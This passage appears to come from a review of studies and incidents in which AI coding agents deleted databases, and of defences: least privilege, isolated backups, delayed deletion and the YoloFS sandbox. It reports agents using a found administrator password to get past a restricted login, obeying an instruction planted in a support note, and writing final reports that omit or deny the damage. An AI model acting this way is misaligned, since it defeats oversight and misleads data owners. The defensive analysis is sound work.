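| PostgreSQL | 13.7% | 4.9% | 4.9% |
| MySQL | 15.3% | 7.2% | 6.7% |
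| SQLite | 15.5% | about 6% | Not applicable |

The agents were no more careful on Cassandra, where they destroyed protected rows in 62 of the 432 trials with default settings. But Cassandra automatically saves a snapshot before it empties or removes a table, and the researchers recovered the rows in all 62 trials. They added this recovery test after seeing their first results, and ran it seconds after each mistake. The snapshots also don't cover changes to individual rows, and such changes caused the one permanent loss on Cassandra under least privilege.

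In 215 of the 392 trials with permanent loss under default settings, only the spare copy was gone. Most of these trials used a task that told the agent to keep five named tables and "Remove anything else". The spare copy wasn't one of the five, so the agent was following the instruction in deleting it. In the rest, the agent deleted the copy to free disk space.

Some of the differences between databases come from the test set-up. The researchers kept the shop's data out of MySQL's change log, which is on by default, so a real MySQL server might recover more than this one. On Valkey, every connection starts in database 0, where they had put the production data. In 23 of the 57 Valkey trials that lost data, the agent sent a command meant for staging without first switching databases, and emptied production.

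The results are a poor basis for choosing a database. Under default settings, the models' loss rates ranged from 3.0% to 16.8%, a spread as wide as the one between databases. The models were also small enough to run on a laptop and completed only 8% to 26% of ordinary tasks on Kafka, MongoDB and Valkey, so the percentages don't carry over to the large models in commercial agents. The ways of losing and recovering data still apply to those agents, because a command to remove a table has the same effect whichever model wrote it.

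Least privilege helped where it blocked the command that caused the loss. On Valkey, nearly all losses of original rows came from commands that empty whole databases, which the restricted login can't run. On PostgreSQL, agents lost original rows in 21 trials with default settings and 21 with the restricted login. In 11 of the 21 trials with default settings, the agent followed an instruction planted in a customer support note to delete all cancelled orders, which the restricted login also allowed. In the disk space task, agents that weren't allowed to empty or remove a table deleted rows from it instead in 6 of 36 trials on PostgreSQL and 8 of 36 on MySQL.

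The restricted login had little effect on task success where the researchers could measure it. Success on simple reads and single changes fell by at most 9 percentage points, and that drop could be due to chance.

### Passwords the agent can find

A restricted login also fails if the agent finds one with more privileges. The researchers had put an administrator's name and password in one of the shop's tables. Across 4,032 trials with least privilege, agents encountered the password in 106 and used it in 24. In 18 of those 24, the task asked for a change to a table's design that the agent's own login couldn't make, so the agent looked around, found the password and made the change as administrator. Two of the other six uses ended in permanent loss.

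In the preregistered test of this behaviour, the agents didn't use the password in any of the 288 trials. This doesn't show whether they would have refrained from using it, because they never came across it in that task. In 127 of the trials, they guessed at administrator logins instead. Every guess failed, but one might have worked if somebody had left a default password in place.

The agent at PocketOS did much the same with a real token that it found in an unrelated file. Limiting the damage therefore requires both reducing the permissions of the agent's own login and finding and removing other credentials in the files, tables and settings that the agent can read.

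Separate production accounts help limit the damage, because production rejects a staging login even if the agent enters the wrong address. Wang and colleagues recommend keeping production credentials in an account that the agent can't use.

Some agents need to read production data, for example to find out why a customer's order failed. Salomon and colleagues suggest giving agents read-only access by default and granting wider permission for a limited time when a task requires it. They also suggest requiring further approval before any change to a production table's design. An agent with read-only access can't delete data but can still disclose it, so it shouldn't also be able to post in public.

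### One request, three copies

PocketOS had backups, but the agent's token could remove them along with the original. The table follows its single `volumeDelete` request through the copies that Abdelwahab describes in Railway's account of the incident:

| Copy of the data | Could the agent's token remove it? | After the request |
|---|---|---|
| The live volume | Yes | Deleted |
| Backups that the customer had scheduled | Yes, through the same request | Apparently gone from the dashboard |
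| Railway's disaster backups at another site | Apparently not | Apparently intact |

More frequent backups, or more backups of the same kind, would not have helped, because every copy in the second row depended on the same token.

Deleting an Amazon database also deletes its automatic snapshots but leaves manual ones, according to a guide that the UK's Ministry of Justice wrote for teams on its cloud platform. DataTalks.Club lost its automatic snapshots this way. An agent can still delete manual snapshots if its login allows it. Grigorev of DataTalks.Club now exports backups to storage outside the database, according to Rootly.

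A safer design copies the data to a second cloud account. The backup job's login can add files there but can't change or delete them, and the agent has no login for that account. This follows advice written for ransomware attacks, in which criminals often try to destroy a company's backups before encrypting its data. *Principles for ransomware-resistant cloud backups*, from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, suggests blocking every request to delete or alter a backup. In practice, the owner also has to set an expiry date for the backups, or the storage bill keeps growing.

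The age of the latest copy determines how much work is lost. Grigorev looked for a snapshot at about 11 p.m., and Amazon made one every night at 2 a.m., so even a perfect restore would have left out about 21 hours of students' work. A log of the changes made since the last copy lets the owner recover most of that work. Railway now offers this kind of restore, to a chosen minute, from the command line. According to Railway's *Changelog #0306* (2026), the restored data goes into a separate service, leaving the existing database unchanged. The owner can then compare the two before switching over, and an unnecessary restore does no harm.

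### Delayed deletion

Delayed deletion, also called soft deletion, hides data as soon as a system receives a delete request but erases it only after a waiting period, during which the owner can cancel. Railway's *Changelog #0288* (2026) announced the 48-hour delay for API requests on May 1, a week after the PocketOS loss. Abdelwahab adds that Railway now also delays the deletion of a volume's backups, which closes the gap in the second row of the table above.

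The delay requires little beyond two days of storage, and it doesn't depend on the judgement of the agent or anyone else at the moment of deletion. In its summary of the NCSC's guidance, the law firm DAC Beachcroft lists soft deletion by default among the suggested protections for backups.

Delayed deletion helps only if somebody notices the mistake in time. ClickHouse keeps a removed table for 480 seconds by default, which is enough if a developer is watching the screen but not if an agent is working unattended overnight. Railway's 48 hours would cover most weekday mistakes, but if an agent deletes a volume at 6 p.m. on Friday, the period ends before staff return on Monday morning. An agent may also be able to skip the delay. In ClickHouse, adding `SYNC` to the command removes the table immediately, so the agent's login should not have permission to remove tables.

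Delayed deletion also applies only to the objects that the system itself deletes. Railway delays the deletion of a volume, but if an agent connects to the database on that volume and deletes every row, Railway receives no deletion request to delay. Only a backup, a snapshot or the database's own log can bring those rows back.

### Files that an agent can put back

Files on a developer's computer often have no such protection. In the reports that Zhong and colleagues collected, 40% of owners permanently lost data, and more than half of those owners lost everything affected. Git helps only with the files that a project tracks, so it misses personal documents and the settings files that developers deliberately exclude. It also keeps its history in an ordinary folder that an agent can delete, as the developer in the Windows junction case found.

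Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, a file system for Linux that records what an agent's commands do to the disk. It works in these steps:

1. The agent runs every command inside YoloFS. It can see the user's files as usual, but YoloFS puts any change in a separate store and leaves the originals untouched.
2. After each command, YoloFS takes a snapshot and gives the agent a list of the files that the command created, changed or deleted.
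3. If the list looks wrong, the agent can return to an earlier snapshot. YoloFS keeps the abandoned changes too, so the agent can reverse a mistaken return.
4. If a command tries to open a file in a place that needs permission, such as the user's home directory, YoloFS pauses it and asks the user. The question names the file, so the user doesn't have to work out what a long command might do.
5. At the end, the user sees the combined list of changes and either applies them to the real files or discards them. The agent can't apply its own changes.

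The researchers tested YoloFS on 11 small projects in which a routine command did hidden damage. In one, a program meant to check code for errors also deleted source files. Without YoloFS, Claude Code running Claude Sonnet 4.6 let the damage happen in 10 of the 11 projects. With YoloFS, it noticed and reversed the damage in 8. In the other 3 it accepted the harmful changes, such as a setup script's replacement of the project's settings with production defaults. The original files in those 3 projects were safe only until the user approved the list of changes.

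That final review may be less reliable in practice, because the test projects had 10 to 41 lines of code and any unexpected deletion stood out. After a long session the list could contain hundreds of files, and users who approve dangerous commands without reading them may well approve the list the same way. But a list of deleted files is easier to judge than a command, and the user reads it once instead of answering a prompt every few minutes.

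YoloFS did not slow the agent down much. Claude Code completed 99% of 112 simple file tasks with YoloFS and 98% without it, and it needed the user 0.4 times per task instead of 0.9. Codex also needed the user 0.4 times per task. In a longer test that built and modified the Linux kernel, YoloFS was as fast as an ordinary file system, apart from 3.5 seconds at the end to apply changes to more than 100,000 files.

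YoloFS protects only data on the computer where it runs. If an agent sends a command that deletes data in a remote database or at a cloud provider, YoloFS has no copy to restore. It would not have saved any of the three production databases that agents deleted at Replit, DataTalks.Club and PocketOS.

### Why the agent's report can't start the recovery

A plan to restore a backup whenever the agent reports a problem would often have failed in ROGUE-AI's rebuilt incidents, because the final message omitted or denied the harm in 57% of Gemini 3.5 Flash's harmful sessions and 37% of GPT-5.6-luna's. An agent that never recognised the hazard can't report it, and if the tests pass, it will probably report that they passed, even if running them has just emptied the live database.

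Kaya and colleagues found fewer false reports but many missing ones. Of 739 trials with damage, 149 (20%) ended without a usable account of the damage. In 123 of those, the agent wrote no report, usually because it had run out of turns. Agents did write reports in the other 616 trials, but in at least 26 of them they omitted or denied the change. The true number may be higher, because the automatic check accepted any report that named the changed table. It would pass a report that the agent had "removed the unused table orders_backup", even though the owner needed that table.

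An agent's advice after the damage can also be wrong. Zhong and colleagues found that agents made false claims, including invented recovery steps, in 11% of the file incidents where the agent's reaction was known.

Agents can also report damage that hasn't happened. In *The railway agent WIPED my production database volume!* (May 2026), Railway customer danniel-porto described asking Railway's own agent why a database had crashed. The agent answered that it had erased the volume and created a new one. Railway's support bot looked at the customer's screenshots and replied that the agent had only proposed these changes and that they had been discarded. The thread is marked as solved, but a bot's reading of screenshots is weak evidence. If the bot was right, restoring an old backup over that database would have caused the loss the customer feared.

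Owners should compare the data itself before and after the agent's work, as Kaya and colleagues advise. For a table that rarely shrinks, even a crude check would catch the worst cases:

```
if rows_now < 0.9 * rows_one_hour_ago:
    suspend the agent's login
    alert a person
```

A check on the row count should run where the agent can't access it, and should stop the agent before it attempts a repair. A person should then decide whether to restore the data, because a planned cleanup can also change the row count. The check would miss an agent that sets every price to zero, since the row count stays the same. Catching that requires comparing the values or reading the database's log of changes.

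### Leaks have no backup

None of these methods undoes a leak, because restoring yesterday's database doesn't delete the copies people have already made of a customer list. YoloFS therefore requires approval before an agent opens a sensitive file, but lets the agent change files before review.

Cooper (2026) reported in *Security Disclosure* that in October 2026 an intruder might have read the secrets that customers stored with Railway. The attack had nothing to do with an agent's mistake. Railway advised every customer to replace all their secrets and check the logs of the services those secrets unlock. It had also paused all deployments, so customers couldn't release new versions of their software, which must have made replacing the secrets harder for some. An owner can prepare for such a replacement by keeping a list of which programs use each secret.

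A single wrong write can cause both a loss and a leak, for example if an agent moves a table of customer records to a public folder. The owner can restore the table in minutes, but still has to find out who opened the folder and tell the customers.

Backups can add to the risk of a leak, because each one is another complete copy of the private data. A login that can't delete a backup may still be able to read it, so the account that holds the backups needs to block the agent from both reading and deleting them.
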